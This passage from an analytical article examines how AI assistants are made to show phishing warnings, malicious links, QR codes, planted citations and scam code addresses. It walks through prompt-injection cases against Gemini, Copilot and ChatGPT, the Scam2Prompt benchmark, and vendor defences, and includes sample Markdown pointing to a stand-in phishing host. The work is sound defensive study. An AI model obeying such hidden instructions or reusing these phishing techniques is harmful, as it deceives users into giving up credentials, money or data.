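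According to Netcraft, a Fudan University study found that AI search engines filtered out 99.78% of traditional SEO attacks, but that techniques designed for AI search (GEO) doubled the rate at which manipulated content reached answers. So GEO can work, but the scammers behind Netcraft's 58 links may not have used it, since an assistant could also pick up a scam page that nobody had adapted for AI.

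With either kind of page, the model may write a misleading link without being told to deceive. It mistakes the scammer's page for the bank's and labels the link with the bank's name. A defence against indirect prompt injection wouldn't help, because the page can mislead the model without containing an injection.

### What real attackers have done

Hiding instructions in content, the attack that researchers have demonstrated most often, also appears in real phishing emails. The security company Barracuda's *Threat Spotlight* (July 2025) described malicious prompts inside harmless-looking emails. The company published more examples in October 2026, which Mascellino (2026) reported in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*.

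*Phishing emails are baiting your AI assistant* (Arntz, 2026) describes phishing emails written for both a human recipient and an AI assistant that might summarise the message. One email contained a password-protected attachment and its password for the recipient, along with hidden instructions for the assistant. Such instructions could make the assistant call the email legitimate or urgent, so that a person who had ignored it would go back to it. Another email contained hidden instructions for the assistant to list changing a supplier's payment details as a priority action in its summary. The senders hid the instructions in code comments, invisible text, encoded passages and zero-width characters.

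Arntz works for the security company Malwarebytes, but his article explains Barracuda's discovery, so it isn't independent confirmation. He also notes that the hidden text may never reach the model, depending on how a tool extracts an email's contents. The emails prove that criminals have tried indirect prompt injection, but not that it worked on any assistant. In these examples, the senders asked for a false recommendation rather than a link, although a sender could ask for a link in the same way.

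Attackers also appear to use AI platforms to publish their own material. Huntress' *The AI Attack Surface* reports incidents over nine months in which attackers used shareable AI content and public mini-apps to trick people into downloading malware. As with the GPTs that Antebi and colleagues built, an outsider creates the mini-apps and users encounter them on a platform they already trust.

Rashid describes a campaign against programmers who use AI coding assistants. The attacker created a fake programming interface for the Solana blockchain that sent users' transactions to the attacker's wallet. To promote it, the attacker wrote tutorials and forum answers and put dozens of projects on GitHub, some under the names of invented developers with photographs and work histories. Netcraft found at least five people who had copied the malicious code into their public projects, and some of those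 projects showed signs of AI coding tools. An assistant could plausibly have suggested the code, but the programmers could also have copied it from a tutorial.

The best-documented case of real attackers' links appearing in chatbot answers is a campaign to mine cryptocurrency on other people's computers, which Microsoft (2026) reported in May. The attackers set up imitation download sites for small programs such as HWMonitor and CrystalDiskInfo, which appeal to people with powerful graphics cards, and pushed the sites up in ordinary search results. In April, Microsoft also saw reports that chatbots had given links to the sites when users asked where to download software. The download contained the real program and a malicious file that secretly installed a remote-access tool, which the attackers could use to add their mining software.

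Microsoft writes that users "may have been directed" to the sites by chatbots. It bases this on the reports and on records from VirusTotal, a service that scans files and web addresses. Those records included chatbot conversations as a possible source of visits. Microsoft shows one chatbot answer with links to the attackers' domains, but says the example doesn't indicate a systemic problem with any particular AI service. It has linked more than 150 malicious domains to the campaign since March 2026, but doesn't say how many of them appeared in chatbot answers or how many victims arrived that way.

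## How do formatting and citations make outside content look like the assistant's own?

When a model repeats text from a web page, the user doesn't see the site's logo, its layout or the domain in the address bar. The app displays the text in the same format as the assistant's own words.

### One format for every author

Suppose a user asks for a summary of a page about a budgeting tool, and an attacker has hidden instructions in that page. The model might write this:

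```
The page describes a budgeting tool and compares its two price plans.

**Account:** We noticed a sign-in from a new device. [Review it](https://collector.test/login)
```

Markdown has no way to show who wrote each part of an answer. If the model composes one paragraph and an attacker dictates the next, both look like parts of the same answer on screen.

Moving text into a chatbot's answer can also change what it seems to mean. On the budgeting tool's page, a line about an account would refer to an account with that tool, but in an answer from ChatGPT or Copilot, the reader is likely to think of the account they are signed in to. The attacker doesn't have to name the company, because the app displays the company's name around the conversation.

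Andi Ahmeti, the Permiso researcher who found the two problems described below, called this a "trust boundary problem" rather than a problem with the model (TechNadu interview, *When Third-Party Content Appears Inside ChatGPT Responses, Trust Gets Transferred Unintentionally*). A trust boundary is a point where material from an untrusted source enters a part of a system that people rely on. Ahmeti assumes some injected instructions will get past the model's defences, since an attacker needs only one that works. He therefore thinks the app should treat a link from a summarised page differently from one the assistant supplied.

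To do that, the app has to identify which links came from the page. It could compare the links in an answer with those in the page it fetched, which would catch a copied address. A warning the model has paraphrased is harder to trace because it may not match any sentence on the page.

### A fake warning with no link

The simplest demonstration needed no link. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes an attack on Gemini for Workspace, the assistant that Google builds into Gmail and its office apps. A researcher had submitted the attack to 0DIN, Mozilla's programme that rewards people for reporting flaws in AI products.

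The attacker writes an ordinary email and adds instructions in white text or at a font size of zero. Gmail displays these instructions as blank space, but when the recipient clicks "Summarize this email", Gemini receives the email's underlying HTML, including the hidden text. It summarises the visible message and then adds the attacker's warning. In Figueroa's example, the warning claims that someone has compromised the user's Gmail password, and gives a phone number to call and a reference number to quote.

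A phone number avoids most of the protections against phishing. An email filter that looks for malicious links and attachments won't find any. The user has no registrable domain to check, and URL reputation lists don't cover phone numbers. If the user calls, the person who answers can ask for their password. Figueroa rates the attack's social impact as moderate, because an attacker could send the email in bulk but each victim still has to ask for a summary and act on it.

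The hidden instructions were inside a tag that made them look like an administrator's. Figueroa says that Gemini gives such text a higher priority, but he doesn't compare the results with and without the tag, so it's unclear whether Gemini would have followed the instructions anyway.

Researchers had reported similar attacks on Gemini in 2024, and Google had already published countermeasures when this one appeared. According to Android Central's *Turns out Gmail's AI email summaries aren't as secure as we thought*, Google said nobody had yet used the trick in a real attack. Tom's Guide reported that Google was still putting some of its countermeasures in place. The case dates from July 2025, so it is weak evidence of how Gemini behaves today. But Permiso's next two studies used the same basic method on other companies' assistants.

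### The same attack in three parts of Copilot

Permiso's *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH* (March 2026) tested three places where office workers can ask Microsoft 365 Copilot to summarize an email. The first is Outlook's "Summarize" button, which puts the summary above the message. The second is a chat pane beside the message. The third is Copilot in Teams, Microsoft's workplace chat and meeting program.

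At first the researchers tried to make Copilot add a harmless film catchphrase in bold at the end of its summary. When the email contained little besides the instruction, Copilot detected it and refused to summarize the email. The researchers then put the instruction at the end of a longer, more natural email, and the results began to differ between the three places.

| Where the user asks for the summary | What Permiso observed |
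|---|---|
| "Summarize" button in Outlook | Refused when the instruction was obvious. With longer emails, it sometimes wrote a normal summary and sometimes included traces of the attacker's text. |
| Copilot pane in Outlook | Usually ignored the instruction or refused to follow it, but complied in some cases, depending on the email program. |
| Copilot in Teams | Most likely to write a normal summary and add the attacker's text. |

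Permiso doesn't explain why a longer email helped the attack. Microsoft's detection may have assessed the message as a whole, so a few suspicious lines counted for less among paragraphs of ordinary business. The results show that defences on the model's side can work, since the Outlook button stopped the obvious version before the app had anything to display. But Microsoft hadn't protected the three places equally, and users have no reason to expect a difference between them. Permiso expects people to use whichever one gives them an answer. If so, a refusal in Outlook could send someone to Teams, where the attack was most likely to succeed.

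The researchers next replaced the catchphrase with a security notice. Copilot summarised the email accurately, then added a section headed "Action Required" that warned of a sign-in from an unrecognised device and offered a "Click here" link styled like a button. An attacker could hide the instruction in the email, as in the Gemini case, so the recipient would see a normal message and an alarming summary.

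This is the transfer of trust that Permiso warns about. People would plausibly believe the notice more readily than an email, especially if their employer has encouraged them to use Copilot. However, Permiso didn't show the notice to any users. It also reports its results in words such as "sometimes" and "in most cases", without saying how many emails it tested or how many attacks succeeded.

In another test, the instruction was to look for material outside the email. Copilot replied that it would search for the recipient's last two Teams messages with a named colleague. Permiso says that in some cases it saw Copilot put recent internal material like this into the attacker's link. The fake notice would then give the user a reason to click, and clicking would leak the material.

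Permiso is more cautious about that last step. It says it confirmed the complete theft "conceptually", and that the outcome would depend on what Copilot could retrieve, how the app displayed the link, and which security controls the company used. The demonstration is therefore stronger evidence that Copilot would display a deceptive notice than that an attacker could reliably steal data with one.

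### How Microsoft fixed it

Microsoft accepted the report quickly. Permiso gives these dates, all in 2026:

- **23 January:** Permiso reported the problem.
- **28 January:** Microsoft confirmed that it had reproduced the behaviour.
- **29 and 30 January:** Microsoft identified contributing factors in how certain apps rendered and handled links, and began work on a fix.
- **17 February:** Microsoft confirmed that it had started to release the fix in phases.
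- **11 March:** Microsoft confirmed that it had finished the release.
- **12 March:** Microsoft published the problem as CVE-2026-26133, and Permiso published its findings.

A CVE number is a software flaw's identifier in an international catalogue of vulnerabilities. Microsoft's advisory for this flaw, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), credits Ahmeti and rates it "Important". According to the advisory, a malicious email could cause Copilot to present "authoritative‑looking phishing messages" with links that leak data or open a malicious site.

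The advisory is useful independent evidence because Microsoft had no commercial reason to exaggerate the problem. It also shows how deception can be filed under another name. Its title mentions only information disclosure, so a security team searching a list of vulnerability titles for phishing would miss it. The advisory includes a question about why the title mentions only that, given that the attack requires the user to do something.

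The completed release didn't necessarily protect everyone at once, because anyone with an older version of an affected app would have to update it. Microsoft marks customer action as required and lists fixed versions of 20 apps. Nineteen are for phones and tablets, including Outlook, Teams, Word and Edge, and the other is Outlook for Mac. The list fits Microsoft's finding that the way apps handled links was part of the cause, but Permiso doesn't say what the updates changed. They might stop Copilot from following the instruction, or they might only stop the app from displaying the result as a working link. Permiso also doesn't report repeating its tests on the fixed versions.

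The public vulnerability record, GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), includes an assessment by the American cybersecurity agency CISA that lists no exploitation of the flaw. CISA made that assessment on 16 March, four days after Permiso published its findings, so it doesn't cover later attacks.

### A fake account alert in ChatGPT

In the ChatGPhish study of May 2026, Permiso planted its instructions in web pages instead of emails. When the researchers opened a page in Firefox and used the browser's menu to ask ChatGPT for a summary, Firefox passed the page's content to ChatGPT. Permiso stresses that this isn't a flaw in Firefox. Any browser tool that summarises pages would have the same problem if its app displayed links and images from those pages without showing their source.

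The researchers added text to the page that looked like a formatting requirement. It required an answer in two parts, the model's normal summary followed by a ready-made notice. ChatGPT summarised a software project on GitHub and then told the user that their account had a new device, a Chrome browser on a Linux computer in Pristina, with a link labelled "Click here".

Details like these resemble the ones in genuine security alerts, which often name a browser and a city. A user may also trust the notice more because it follows a real summary. Someone who knew the project could confirm that the summary was correct before reading the notice. An attacker who replaced the whole answer with a warning would lose that advantage.

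In a test, Permiso's own web page contained an article about Kosovo, with the instructions near the end of its HTML. The link appeared under the heading "Additional Resources". That version didn't try to frighten anyone, and it resembles the quietly suggested link that Greshake and colleagues considered more dangerous than open persuasion.

### Why a QR code moves the click to a phone

In another version, the researchers put a QR code in the notice instead of a text link. The attacker makes the code and puts a picture of it online. The instructions on the page make the model write a Markdown image with the picture's address, and the ChatGPT app fetches the picture and displays it in the answer. When the user scans the code with a phone, the phone opens the address stored in the code.

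The desktop browser handles only the picture's address, so the computer's usual checks on links never reach the address inside the code.

Hovering over the code may even falsely reassure users. In Permiso's example, the image was also a link to its own picture file, which the researchers had stored with Amazon's cloud service. A user who checked the link's destination would have seen an Amazon address, but scanning the code with a phone would have opened a different one.

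Some checks still apply when someone scans the code. Many phones show at least part of an address before they open it, and a phone's browser may have its own blocklist. A password manager on the phone can also detect that a site doesn't match the saved one. But an employee may scan the code with a personal phone, which the employer's security software doesn't cover, and a small preview has little room for a long address.

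It is also unclear how many people would scan a code that appeared in a summary, and Permiso's tests don't settle this. Picking up a phone takes more effort than clicking a link, and the request could seem odd. But many services ask people to scan a code to sign in or link a device, so a notice about a new device gives the code a believable purpose.

Ahmeti told TechNadu that apps should treat QR codes as encoded web addresses, not as harmless pictures. This is technically possible because software can decode a QR code as easily as a phone can. The app would have to scan each image for codes before displaying it, then check any address it found as it would any other link.

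The researchers also tried an image whose address used a link shortener. The shortener forwarded the app's request to the researchers' server, which recorded the visit. An app that checked only the first domain would have checked the shortener's and not the server's. Permiso notes that an attacker could use such a record to learn that a particular target had read a particular page through ChatGPT, which would help in planning a follow-up attack. Ahmeti said he was most surprised by how little the user had to do, since in some tests asking for the summary was enough to trigger the request.

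### How OpenAI handled the report

OpenAI responded very differently from Microsoft. Permiso sent its first report on 29 April 2026 through Bugcrowd, a service that companies use to receive reports of security flaws. The next day OpenAI marked it "Not Reproducible" because the instructions for repeating the attack weren't detailed enough. On 1 May Permiso sent a new version with more steps and screenshots. It also removed from the title a claim about cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's code runs inside a web page, and the published study doesn't demonstrate such an attack.

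OpenAI first classed the new report as "Not Applicable" and later as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso asked on 7 May to discuss the wider impact further, and published its findings on 29 May. Origo's *Riasztást adtak ki, súlyosan sebezhető a ChatGPT* (2026), a Hungarian news article based on a report in The Register, says the researchers disputed that their report was a duplicate but got no reply. OpenAI didn't answer The Register's questions either.

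Outsiders can't tell whether the report was a duplicate, because companies don't normally publish the reports they receive. If it was, someone had already told OpenAI about the problem, and ChatGPT was still displaying the components when Permiso tested it. If it wasn't, OpenAI closed a new report without resolving it. The Copilot findings have firmer support because Microsoft reproduced them, while the ChatGPT findings rest on Permiso's own screenshots and server records.

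Two days after Permiso published, eWeek concluded in *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* that OpenAI didn't appear to have fixed the problem. The publication inferred this from Permiso's dates and didn't test ChatGPT. None of these accounts includes a test from after May 2026, so they don't show whether ChatGPT still behaves this way. OpenAI could have changed the model or the app without announcing it.

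The interim advice to users was of limited help. eWeek suggested avoiding ChatGPT summaries of web pages, which would work but mean giving up the feature. According to Origo, the researchers recommended caution about unexpected warnings and links in answers. That might protect people from the account alert, but they would expect to see a link under "Additional Resources".

### Strangers' pages on the assistant's own site

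Criminals also make their content look like the assistant's own by publishing it on the assistant's website. They don't need an injection, because anyone can use the site's sharing features.

Keverenge (2026) reports in *A real ChatGPT page is being used to trick people into installing malware* that researchers at Huntress found a custom GPT called "Plus 5.6" on the real ChatGPT site. It sent users to a page that imitated a security check by Cloudflare, which many websites use to block automated visitors. The page tricked users into running a Windows command that could install malware with access to their files, screen, webcam and microphone. The name "Plus 5.6" helped the attackers pass the GPT off as an official OpenAI product.

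The security company Push Security found a similar campaign that used ChatGPT's ability to display web pages from code. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Abuse Shared Content for ChatGPT Phishing Campaign*, the attackers made a ChatGPT-branded page where they claimed the service was down because of heavy traffic. They told visitors to download the desktop app instead and linked to a fake download site. People reached the first page through malicious Google adverts and manipulated search results.

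The registrable domain of that first page was chatgpt.com. OpenAI hosted the page but a stranger wrote it, so checking the domain would not have revealed the writer, as with the Wells Fargo imitation on Google Sites. Push Security warns that most scanning tools also trust the address. The second page was harder to examine because it showed the fake download to ordinary visitors and something harmless to automated scanners.

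In another campaign, reported by Infosecurity Magazine, attackers shared a chat disguised as a guide to installing Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant, on a Mac and attributed it to "Apple Support". The chat contained a command that downloaded and ran malware. Shared chats are especially convenient for this kind of deception because a person can steer an assistant into writing almost any instructions, then publish them in the format that readers associate with the assistant's help.

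Push Security found these pages in its customers' systems, so unlike the Permiso studies, they are evidence of real attacks. They suggest that criminals value an assistant's address and appearance. But the victims came to a public page through a search engine or an advert, so we can't tell from these attacks how people would react to a fake notice in an answer to their own question. They might be more trusting, or they might realize that the notice had nothing to do with what they asked.

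### Citations as signs of trust

A citation can make an answer more convincing even if nobody opens it. A small number, site name or file title beside a sentence suggests that the assistant has checked the sentence against a source. Readers can rely on the citation only if the source exists, supports the sentence and is trustworthy.

MITRE's ATLAS entry on citations lists three ways for an attacker to manipulate them, and each breaks one of those conditions. Suppose an answer claims that Example Bank charges nothing for transfers abroad, which is false:

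- **A wrong citation.** The answer cites a real page on the bank's site that gives its opening hours. The page exists but doesn't mention transfers.
- **An invented citation.** The answer cites a page of fees that the bank never published, so the link leads to an error message.
- **A real citation of planted data.** The answer cites a "guide to bank fees" that the attacker wrote and put online. The page exists and contains exactly the claim in the answer.

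A reader can discover the first two by opening the source. With planted data, opening the source makes the false claim more convincing, because the page repeats it. The reader has to ask who wrote the page and whether they would know, and the citation gives little help with that. For example, anyone who followed a citation to the technology journalist's hot-dog page would have found the claim there.

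If a citation's domain is invented, an attacker can also register it and plant a page there that supports the claim.

A model can produce bad citations even when nobody has manipulated it. It can attach the wrong source to a sentence or mistake a scammer's page for a reliable one.

### The planted bank details of 2024

The best-known demonstration of misplaced trust in sources predates the ATLAS entry. In August 2024, Michael Bargury, a co-founder of Zenity and former Microsoft security architect, presented five attacks on Copilot at Black Hat, a large US security conference. *Microsoft’s AI Copilot can be weaponized as an ‘automated phishing machine’* (Lazzaro, 2024), a Fortune article, summarises the attacks from the slides and demonstration videos.

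Unlike several of the other attacks, the one about payments didn't require the attacker to take over someone's email account first. The attacker sends an employee an email that gives the attacker's bank details as those of a company the employee pays. The email can sit in the inbox until the employee asks Copilot for that company's details. Copilot searches the employee's messages, finds the email and presents the attacker's account number as the answer.

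The change of format helps even this simple version of the attack. An email with new bank details is a familiar warning sign, and many finance departments tell staff to confirm such changes by phone. When Copilot gives the same details in reply to a question, the employee may not realise that they came from an email. A citation naming the email and its sender could have prevented the mistake, provided the employee looked at it.

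In the version behind the ATLAS entry, Copilot cites a reputable-looking file instead, which removes that safeguard. In MITRE's terms, citing a genuine file that doesn't contain the number would be a wrong citation, whereas citing the attacker's email would be a real citation of planted data.

Lazzaro doesn't mention the manipulated source, and she says clearly that Bargury's attacks were demonstrations, not evidence that criminals were using Copilot this way. Microsoft's head of AI incident detection said the company was working with Bargury to address the weaknesses. The demonstrations are now two years old, but they still matter because they led to a recognised category of attack.

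D3FEND, MITRE's catalogue of defences, repeats the definition of deceptive citations but hasn't yet connected it to any of the digital objects it uses to match attacks with defences. Neither Bargury's demonstration nor the ATLAS definition gives a rate at which citations mislead people. Netcraft's 2026 test of four assistants doesn't either, because it counted malicious links, so a harmless page unrelated to the sentence beside it would have passed. Measuring bad citations would require opening each source and comparing it with the claim it was meant to support.

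## Which parts of an answer are checked before it is shown?

The app can check an answer after the model writes it and before the user sees it. Each of the usual checks covers one aspect, such as the meaning of the words or the reputation of a web address, so it can miss a component that is deceptive in some other way.

### What each check looks at

Four checks matter most for deceptive components:

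- **Moderation classifier.** This is a model that labels text as harmful or harmless by its content, using categories such as violence, hate and self-harm.
- **URL reputation list.** This is a maintained list of addresses known to be malicious, such as Google Safe Browsing. The app looks up an address and learns whether it is on the list.
- **Removal by the renderer.** While converting the Markdown, the renderer can leave something out, for instance by refusing to load images from other companies' servers.
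- **Comparison of label and destination.** The app checks whether a link's label names a different site from the one the link opens.

The table shows what each check can examine in each part of an answer. An app may use only one or two of these checks.

| Part of the answer | Moderation classifier | URL reputation list | Removal by the renderer | Comparison of label and destination |
|---|---|---|---|---|
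| Prose | Its meaning | Nothing | Usually nothing | Nothing |
| Link label | Its meaning, along with the prose | Nothing | Usually nothing | Any domain in the label |
| Destination | The characters of the address, but not the page | The address | The address, and it can delete the link | The registrable domain |
| Image address | The characters of the address | The address | The address, and it can refuse to load the image | Nothing |
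| Image content | The picture, if the classifier accepts images and the app sends them | Nothing | Nothing, though blocking the image removes its content too | Nothing, even if the picture contains words |
| Code | Its text | Addresses in the code, if the app extracts them | Usually nothing | Nothing, since an address in code has no label |
| Citation | The sentence and the source's title | The source's address | The address, and it can delete the link | Any domain in the visible text |

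None of these checks opens a cited page to see whether it supports the sentence beside it. Only the classifier would have anything to examine in the fake Gmail warning that Figueroa described, and that warning read like an ordinary security notice.

Text-based checks are more likely to miss image content than any other part of an answer, and researchers have also tested it less. For example, Kong and colleagues say their benchmark doesn't cover malicious addresses inside images.

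### Why a polite sentence can pass a classifier

Suppose a model writes one of these two lines:

```
The bank has new terms. Please [sign in](https://bank.example/login) to accept them.
The bank has new terms. Please [sign in](https://collector.test/login) to accept them.
```

Only the domain differs. The wording is polite and fits none of the usual categories of harmful text. Whether collector.test is a phishing site depends on who registered it and what page its server sends, and the line contains neither fact.

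A classifier may have learned some malicious addresses during training, but attackers can register new ones afterwards. Developers can train a model to distrust odd-looking addresses, as Kong and colleagues did with URLGuard, but such a model is less likely to catch an ordinary-looking one like `collector.test/login`. General-purpose models have the same difficulty, which helps explain why ChatGPT missed the phishing link when Antebi and colleagues asked it to review the transcript.

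### A $2,500 loss

The most detailed test of this weakness concerns addresses in code. In November 2024, a user asked ChatGPT for a script to buy a cryptocurrency token. ChatGPT wrote a script for the wrong blockchain, Ethereum, and then a general script for the right one, Solana. Both were harmless. The user then specified that the script had to buy from pump.fun, a legitimate trading platform.

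Pump.fun had no official programming interface for trading. ChatGPT wrote code that used a scammer's interface instead and sent it the user's private key, which gives complete control over the money in the wallet. The code had errors, so the user went back to ChatGPT several times to fix them. Within 30 minutes of running the final version, the user had lost everything in the wallet, about $2,500.

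The scammers had published instructions for their interface on GitHub, Stack Exchange and other sites that programmers use, much as in the Solana campaign that Rashid describes. *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2026), a paper at the machine-learning conference ICML, investigates whether the incident was a rare accident.

These results show how models and moderation tools handle a malicious address surrounded by harmless text. They don't cover misleading labels, because the addresses studied were ones that a program contacts when it runs, not links that a person clicks.

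### How the researchers built the prompts

The researchers worked backwards from real scam sites:

1. They took two public lists of scam addresses, one with 187,555 entries and one with 119,828. They kept the 28,570 pages that were still online and had readable text.
2. They gave the visible text of each page to a language model, which wrote short programming requests using specific terms from the page. Three models did this and produced 265,114 prompts.
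3. They gave the prompts to four models that the paper dates to 2024 (GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3) and asked for working code.
4. They extracted every address from the code and looked it up with three detectors, ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup. A program counted as malicious if any detector flagged any address in it.

The models wrote more than a million programs. The share containing a malicious address averaged 4.24% across 12 combinations of a prompt-writing model and a code-writing model, and ranged from 3.19% to 5.94%. The rate for ordinary programming requests is probably much lower, since every prompt came from a scam site.

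The researchers then built a harder test from the 3,150 prompts that had produced malicious code from all four models. They kept all 1,159 that contained no known scam address, added 400 chosen at random from the rest, and had three of the paper's authors check that each was a plausible request from a programmer. The three rejected 182, which left a benchmark of 1,377 prompts called Innoc2Scam-bench. About half concern cryptocurrency, and the rest cover subjects such as online shops, finance and travel.

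### Results for seven models from 2025

Chen and colleagues gave the benchmark to seven newer models:

| Model | Malicious code, share of all prompts | Blocked by a content filter | Malicious code, share of completed programs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 40.2% | 22.3% |
| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 1.7% | 24.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 8.4% | 37.8% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 1.3% | 44.1% |
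| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 0.1% | 45.3% |
| Qwen3 Coder | 45.6% | 0.2% | 45.9% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 47.3% | 0.9% | 47.9% |

Gemini 2.5 Pro's lead over GPT-5 came mainly from refusing to answer. On the 637 prompts that all seven models completed, the gap was small enough to be due to chance. A refusal protects the user, but a filter that blocks 40% of requests that reviewers considered normal could be hard to work with.

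The researchers describe these as stress-test rates. They chose the prompts because four earlier models had failed on them, so 47.3% doesn't mean that nearly half of DeepSeek's code contains scam addresses.

Prompt selection may also have exaggerated the failures of the original four models. The benchmark included only prompts that GPT-4o had failed, but when the researchers retested the model in November 2025, it failed on 50.04% of them. They suggest that OpenAI had updated the model in the meantime. Some prompts might also have produced a malicious address only by chance the first time.

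Other changes made little difference. Asking GPT-4o to break the task into parts, or showing it examples of good answers, left its rate at about 50%. Three sizes of Google's Gemma 3 had rates between 34.9% and 41.6%. In the original experiment, two OpenAI models still had rates of 4.19% to 5.09% with more randomness in their output.

### Did the models remember the scams or guess the addresses?

Chen and colleagues conclude that scam material has contaminated the models' training data, because all four original models produced 2,029 of the same malicious domains even though three different companies had trained them. Six of the seven newer models also did slightly worse on prompts that contained no scam address, so the models weren't simply copying addresses from the request.

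Another possible explanation is that the four models guessed the scam sites' addresses from the prompts. The researchers had told the prompt-writing models to use distinctive keywords from each page, and several of the published prompts include a scam's brand name. One asks for code to check in for a flight through a named travel site. A model that had never encountered the site could guess its address by adding a common suffix to the name. Because all four models answered the same prompts, they could have made the same guesses.

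The model probably memorised some of these addresses from its training data and guessed others. In either case, the user receives code that contacts a scammer's server. Cleaning the training data would remove memorised addresses but might not prevent guesses.

An outside review, *Refusal Evaluation in Coding LLMs and Code Agents* (2026), reports a slightly different range, 12.7% to 43.8%. It covers an earlier version of the benchmark with 1,559 prompts, 182 more than the current one. It also notes that the labels came from automated detectors, with no measure of agreement among human reviewers.

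The *Scam2Prompt* (2026) project page lists results only for the seven models from 2025. Developers have since released newer models, so these rates are weak evidence about current assistants.

### How the moderation tools performed

The researchers next gave the malicious code to tools that developers use to screen a model's output. OpenAI's Moderation API, a service that labels text by category of harm, flagged none of the 3,452 malicious outputs. Llama Guard 3, a classifier from Meta, flagged 291, or 8.43%. (The results for the seven models add up to 3,441 malicious programs, but the difference is too small to matter here.)

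Llama Guard 3 did better when it received the prompt and the code together, flagging 517 of the 3,452 pairs, or about 15%. Some requests had suspicious subjects, such as hiding where Bitcoin came from, which may have helped, but a request about flights wouldn't provide that clue.

The researchers also tested NeMo Guardrails, a safety toolkit from NVIDIA, with a classifier called Llama Nemotron Safety Guard V2. To the classifier's instructions, they added a category covering the use of a scam website or programming interface. It still caught only eight malicious programs in total, between 0% and 0.7% for each model, and labelled all eight as criminal planning rather than use of a scam site. The added category described what to look for, but the classifier had no way to check which addresses were scams.

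Web search could supply that information. In another test, GPT-4o searched the web and was told to check whether the addresses in its code were safe before giving the code to the user. Its rate of malicious output fell from 50.04% to 29.41%. The experiment added the search and the instruction together, so it doesn't show how much each contributed.

The improvement is large, but the remaining failures show the limits of leaving the decision to the model. In some, the search found nothing and GPT-4o used the address anyway. In others, the results didn't clearly identify the scam, or they did and GPT-4o still didn't refuse.

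Chen and colleagues recommend a more direct check, in which the app extracts the addresses from the code and looks them up before the user receives the code. They write that, to their knowledge, no production model did this. However, they tested models through a programming interface rather than the chat apps people normally use, and an app could remove some of these addresses before displaying an answer.

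### What a URL reputation list can miss

The benchmark can't show how well such a lookup would work. The researchers counted an address as malicious if at least one of their three detectors flagged it, so the same three detectors would catch every malicious program in the test. A scam site that none of the detectors had listed would count as harmless, both in the test and in a real app.

Some scam sites escape the lists. During the study, the researchers reported scam domains missing from the database of MetaMask, a crypto wallet company, which accepted 62 of them. The researchers infer that these sites had been active for more than a year, because the four original models' training data ended by August 2024. This assumes that the models learned the addresses from that data rather than guessing them.

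Lists can also give different results for the same address. In their slides for the conference, Chen and colleagues show an address for a Bitcoin service that ChainPatrol and SecLookup rated malicious and Google Safe Browsing rated safe. Their paper records Google's result for that address as an unknown threat, so it's unclear what Google's list returned. An app that relied on one list could still miss an address that another had flagged.

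Attackers can use a new site before it is added to a list. They can also put a page on a reputable domain, as the scammer did with the Wells Fargo imitation on Google Sites. A list would then need to include the individual page, since blocking all of google.com would also block many legitimate pages.

Using more lists would catch more sites but would also add each list's mistakes. Chen and colleagues note that criminals can temporarily take over a legitimate site, and a list may keep flagging it after the owner has recovered it.

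### How companies began to restrict images

The earliest known restrictions in chat apps were meant to prevent data leaks. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a security researcher recalls reporting to OpenAI and Microsoft in 2023 that their chatbots could leak data through images. Microsoft responded that May by changing a setting on the Bing Chat website that controls which servers the browser may load images from. This generally blocked outside images, whatever the model wrote.

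In *A New Era in LLM Security*, Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2024) examined ChatGPT running on GPT-4 and found two protections. OpenAI had instructed the model not to write Markdown images with outside addresses, and a "Safe URL Check" was supposed to stop the app from sending private data through a link or image. The researchers got around both and built a web page that could steal a user's chat history when the user asked ChatGPT to open it.

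They also found that the app displayed images without checking their content. If an attacker got the model to write the address of a pornographic picture, the app displayed it. A check on the model's text would not have examined the picture, because the text contained only its address.

These findings describe ChatGPT in early 2024, and OpenAI has since developed the check it applies when a link opens. They still illustrate why an instruction to the model is a weak substitute for a check in the app. An attacker who can get a model to ignore one instruction may be able to get it to ignore another, but the renderer applies the same rule whatever the model writes.

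### What Google and Microsoft remove

*Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (Google, 2025) describes two measures for Gemini. The renderer doesn't display images from outside addresses. Google also looks for suspicious links, partly with Safe Browsing, and removes them. In the paper's example, Gemini summarises an email thread that contains an unsafe link, and the summary shows "suspicious link removed" in place of the address.

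The image rule would stop both the leaking images and the QR codes that Permiso demonstrated in ChatGPT, if the codes came from an outside server. It would also remove the picture of a "Sign in" button in example 10, though Google doesn't say what happens to a link wrapped around a blocked image. The link check doesn't depend on the label, so it could remove a link called "Click here" as easily as one that names a bank, but only if Google has already identified the destination as suspicious.

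Google published this account in June 2025, a month before Figueroa described the fake Gmail warning. That attack needed no image or link, so neither measure applied to it. Google's other defences include classifiers that check the emails and files the model reads for malicious instructions, before it writes an answer.

Research by the security company Tenable gives some outside support for Google's claims. In *The Trifecta*, its researchers found that Gemini filtered or restricted images and links, and sent links through a google.com address. Sending links through Google could make it harder for users to judge where a link leads, because hovering over it may show Google's domain first.

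Microsoft's (2025) description of its defences against indirect prompt injection is less specific. Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to work, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail. A classifier is probabilistic, while a rule that the app never loads an outside image is deterministic, as long as the app applies it to every image.

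Microsoft says it used a deterministic block to stop a leak through Markdown images, then took similar steps against other leaks, including "the generation of certain untrusted links". It doesn't explain how it decides which links to trust, or what the user sees when it blocks one.

The account mentions phishing links only in messages that an assistant sends to a user's colleagues, not in the assistant's own answers. Microsoft had to address phishing links in answers eight months later, when it fixed the flaw that Permiso found in Copilot.

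Filters also have to recognise a link before they can remove it. *EchoLeak* (2025) describes an attack on Copilot in which the filter missed a link written in one of Markdown's alternative formats. The security company Checkmarx says that Copilot Chat and Gemini were vulnerable to leaks through image requests and other displayed content. This conflicts with Microsoft's and Google's assurances about images, so the two companies' accounts are better evidence of what they meant to block than of what they always blocked.

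### A rule for comparing label and destination

Neither company mentions comparing a link's label with its destination, although some email programs do this. A simple version for a chat app could work as follows:

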